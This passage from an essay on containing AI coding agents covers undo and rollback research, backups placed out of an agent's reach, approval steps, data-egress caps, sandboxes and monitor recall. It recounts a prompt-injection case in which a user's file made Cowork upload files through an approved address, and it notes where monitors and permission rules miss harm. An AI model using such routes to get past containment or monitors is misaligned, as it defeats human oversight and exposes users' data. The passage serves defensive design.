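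Staging doesn't suit every command. An agent may need a server's reply to a push before it can continue, and some services offer no preview. The system can also change between the preview and the real run. A preview that lists one volume for deletion helps only if the reviewer knows or can find out what the volume contains.

### Can people and agents undo the damage?

Delayed deletion hides data at once but erases it only after a waiting period. Since the PocketOS incident, Railway has applied its 48-hour delay to deletions through the API as well as the website. The delay requires extra storage and keeps data that the customer may have good reason to erase. It also doesn't protect data deleted inside a volume that still exists, such as the schema dropped in *accidental DROP SCHEMA CASCADE on production Postgres, no dashboard backup*.

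*Can You Undo It?* (Waghmare and Sufi, 2026) sets three conditions for restoring a previous state exactly. Somebody must have saved the complete state, the agent's account must be able to restore it without another person's help, and no outsider can have seen or acted on the changed version. A leaked customer list fails the third condition even if backups exist.

Their experiments also show that an undo can destroy later work. The researchers had an agent edit a file, added another person's later edit, and then tried to reverse the agent's edit. Restoring the copy saved before the agent's edit erased the other person's work in all four versions of the test. A method that compared the saved, edited and current files removed only the agent's edit when the two edits were in separate paragraphs. When both edits affected the same line, it left the file unchanged so that someone could resolve the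 conflict.

Undoing Git commits caused a similar problem. After a colleague had added a newer commit, the documented command for undoing the agent's commit removed the colleague's commit from the branch instead. Checking first that the agent's commit was still the newest prevented this.

Chen and colleagues compared Cordon with Git as a way to recover from five scripted failures, with 15 trials for each method. After each recovery, they checked whether the task could continue.

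| Recovery method | Median leftover file differences | Task could continue |
|---|---|---|
| Cordon | 0 | 15 of 15 |
| Git restore | 73 | 0 of 15 |
| Git reset | 73 | 0 of 15 |
| Git reset and clean | 0 | 12 of 15 |

Git restore and reset left behind files that Git did not track. A clean-up step removed them, but Git still failed to restore file permissions in one of the five scenarios. These results suggest that a company should save the relevant state before the agent acts, instead of relying on Git to reconstruct it afterwards.

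Some systems prepare to undo an agent's actions. *POLAR* (2026) describes SagaLLM, which plans a set of reversing actions in advance and runs them in reverse order if a task fails, and STRATUS, which keeps a list of executed actions for a separate agent to undo. *POLAR* objects that people can audit the rollback in these systems only after it has run.

Relying on an agent to notice and repair its own mistake is riskier. *Lost in Recovery* (2026) tested agents that operate a computer's graphical interface. Without explicit recovery instructions, the agents restored earlier states less than 1% of the time on average. General-purpose models did much better when prompted to recover, so they had some ability to recover but rarely used it unprompted.

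Retries can also cause damage. *UndoBench* (2026) tested recovery separately from ordinary task skill in 5,760 runs and found severe duplicate effects when confirmation of a successful action was lost. For example, a payment agent that received no confirmation could send the same payment twice. The runs covered only 12 independent groups of tasks, so they don't establish how often this happens in general.

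Developers seldom publish the figures a company would need to compare recovery systems. *Always-On Agents* (2026), a survey of 435 works on agents that keep information over time, found 27 that dealt with rollback. None reported how often recovery succeeded, how much data it lost or what it cost.

### Backups the agent cannot delete

A backup doesn't help if the command that deletes the data also deletes the backup, as happened at PocketOS. ScyllaDB, a database company, used to erase a cluster's nightly backups when a customer deleted the cluster. It now keeps them for one day by default, or up to 60 days if the customer chooses. But customers can disable this retention through the same programming interface that deletes the cluster, so an agent with broad enough access could disable it too.

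It is safer to keep backups in a separate account that the agent's credentials can't reach. After the PocketOS incident, sungkhum asked Railway what it would change, in *Any changes to protect database backups from volume delete?* One reply described adding a further safeguard to the standard volume backups and called for access tokens with narrower permissions.

With nightly backups, an accident can still destroy up to 24 hours of work, or 12 hours on average if accidents are equally likely at any time. More frequent backups reduce the loss but need more storage and processing. Restoring data also takes time, and a backup that nobody has tested may not work. Each copy of customer data is also another place it can leak from.

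The most useful backup for `git reset --hard` would be an automatic copy of the folder's uncommitted edits, made just before the reset. For a small project, the copy would take little time or storage, and no monitor would have to work out whether the user wanted to keep the edits. The agent should not be able to delete the copy as part of the same clean-up.

### Approval by a second person

The joint guidance recommends human approval for actions where a mistake would do serious damage, including system resets, deletion of critical records and outgoing network connections. The system's designers or operators, not the agent, should decide which actions need approval. The guidance also recommends holding any request to delete logs until a person has reviewed it.

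Anthropic's *Activating AI Safety Level 3 Protections* (2025) describes a stricter rule for employees who need access to model weights. An employee must use a physical security key, give a reason and get a second person's permission, and the access expires automatically. A single compromised account is therefore less likely to expose the weights.

Requiring a second person's approval takes another employee's time and may delay an urgent repair at night. It also fails if the approver has no more information than the monitor or approves everything out of habit. An approver reading the same prompts might do no better than the professional testers in Anthropic's study.

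People may look more closely at decisions they make less often. Anthropic reports that Claude Code users reject 39% of the plans the agent presents, compared with 3% of permission prompts. Users can reject a plan because it is inefficient or incomplete, so the difference doesn't measure how well they detect harm. Still, it supports asking users to approve a whole production change, with a preview, instead of each command in it. Anthropic still recommends human review of high-stakes production changes, even with auto mode.

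### Large files and small secrets

A limit on outgoing data works much better for model weights than for passwords. At a cap of 1 gigabyte a day, sending 1 terabyte of weights takes about 1,000 days. If someone detected the transfer after ten days, only about 1% of the weights would have left. Compression could shorten the transfer, as could using several connections if each had its own cap.

An agent could send out a 32-byte key in its first network message. The same daily cap would allow more than 31 million such keys, ignoring the extra bytes needed to send them. A cap low enough to stop one key would also stop almost all useful traffic.

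In May 2025 Anthropic announced limits on how fast data could leave the secure systems that held its model weights. It called the limits preliminary and did not publish the rate. It expected to lower them over time until it would be very difficult for a thief to take the weights before being detected. To set the limits, Anthropic also had to learn where its data was going, which helped it detect unusual traffic. The company thought it might eventually have to move the weights to networks with no outside connection.

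In 2026, Anthropic described changes concerning where its agent products could send data. Claude Cowork could connect only to approved internet addresses, including Anthropic's own service, which it needed to work. An outsider reported that malicious instructions in a user's file could make Cowork upload other files to a different Anthropic account. The upload went through because Anthropic's service was on the approved list.

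Anthropic then placed a proxy inside the virtual machine. The proxy accepts requests to Anthropic's service only if they carry that session's own token. An approved destination is therefore safe only if the company also controls which accounts and functions the agent can use there. A rule for `git push` would have to allow a particular repository, because allowing all of GitHub would include strangers' repositories.

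Keeping secrets away from the agent is more dependable than trying to recognise them as they leave. In Cowork, the user's credentials stay in the computer's password store, outside the virtual machine. The virtual machine receives a limited token for the session, and the company can revoke that token without changing the user's own credentials. More generally, a separate program can attach a key to an approved request so that the agent can use a service without reading the key. The agent could still misuse the service through that program, but it couldn't give the key to anyone else.

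Replacing keys often limits the damage if one leaks. A stolen key that expires in an hour is much less useful than one that lasts for months, although an automated thief may need only seconds. Frequent replacement can interrupt programs that still use the old keys, and it doesn't help if a customer list leaks, because the company can't replace its customers' names and addresses.

### Better recall or a smaller blast radius?

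The benefit of limiting damage can be compared with the benefit of a better monitor in terms of expected loss. If nᵢ is the yearly number of harmful actions of type i, rᵢ is the monitor's recall on them and Lᵢ is the average loss from one that gets through, then

expected yearly loss = Σ nᵢ(1 − rᵢ)Lᵢ

Suppose a company's agents take a million actions a year, of which 10 are harmful. Eight are deletions that would cost $50,000 each, and two are leaks that would cost $300,000 each. The monitor catches 83% of each type. All these figures are invented except the 83%, which is the recall Anthropic first measured for Claude Code's reviewer on overreach.

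| Change | Expected yearly loss |
|---|---|
| None | $170,000 |
| Recall rises to 90% | $100,000 |
| Undo reduces the cost of each deletion to $2,000 | About $105,000 |
| Approved destinations stop nine in ten of the leaks that the monitor misses | About $78,000 |
| Undo and approved destinations together | About $13,000 |
| Undo, approved destinations and 90% recall | About $7,600 |

Undo alone saves slightly less than better recall because it does nothing about leaks. Combined with approved destinations, it saves far more. Without these measures, the monitor would need about 98.7% recall to achieve the same result. Confirming that figure would require the monitor to catch roughly 230 real harmful actions without a miss, and at this base rate the company would need about 23 million actions to collect that many. The company can test an undo system much sooner by deleting and restoring a test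 database.

The two measures save about $157,000 a year before their own costs. On these assumptions, they are worth using only if storage, staff time and delayed work cost less than that. Better recall has drawbacks too, especially for ambiguous actions, where catching more harm may require stopping more harmless work.

The result also depends heavily on rare, severe losses. If one leak in a hundred cost $30 million instead of $300,000, the average leak would cost nearly $600,000. A company might then reasonably remove the agent's access to the data, even if the agent could no longer do some of its work.

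### The dispute over isolation

Simon Willison, a software developer who writes about AI security, argues for relying on enforced limits. When Anthropic introduced auto mode in March 2026, he distrusted AI-based protection against prompt injection because its decisions can vary. He wanted coding agents to run by default in a sandbox that restricts files and network connections with fixed rules. By August, Willison accepted that auto mode was better than constantly asking people for approval, but pointed out that it still missed 11% of dangerous commands in Anthropic's study. He thought the better goal was a productive way to run agents without access to data or tools that could cause harm.

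Developers argue that restrictions don't protect anyone once users switch them off. Trębacz and colleagues report that frequent approval requests lead some people to use Codex's Full Access mode, which removes the sandbox. Others write exceptions that are too broad. In OpenAI's internal traffic, a sizable minority allowed every command beginning with `python`, which can run almost any program.

Anthropic found similar behaviour among Claude Code users. As of June 2026, 49.5% of active users of the command-line version had written a rule to pre-approve some shell commands. Anthropic says 5% allowed every shell command and another 43% had rules almost as broad. A quarter of interactive sessions started with permission checks bypassed. Auto mode therefore ignores rules broad enough to let an agent run arbitrary code without review.

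Both companies used these figures to promote their reviewers, and the figures don't show how much harm users suffered. Some users may have bypassed the checks inside a disposable virtual machine, where that can be reasonable. But even critics are tempted to bypass them. In *Living dangerously with Claude*, Willison describes getting "enormous value" from coding agents with as few restrictions as possible, while being deeply concerned about the risks.

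The evidence shows that people avoid repeated approval prompts, but not that they would reject a sandbox that lets them do their normal work. Claude Code's sandbox removed most prompts, and most actions in OpenAI's illustration never had to leave the sandbox. Well-chosen limits can therefore make an agent safer and more convenient.

Willison has also complained that sandbox makers rarely document their sandboxes well enough for users to judge how far to trust them. In *How we contain Claude across products*, a commentary on Anthropic's article of the same name, Willison (2026) praised Anthropic for explaining its methods in detail. The failures in Anthropic's article show why the details matter, since an approved address or an unchecked link can undo much of a sandbox's protection.

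A reviewer is still useful for actions that have to cross the boundary, such as a requested push to an outside repository. If too many routine actions need review, OpenAI advises users to adjust the sandbox first by adding specific folders or narrow command rules. It warns against allowing all `python` or `curl` commands, because such broad rules can remove the boundary the reviewer is supposed to guard.
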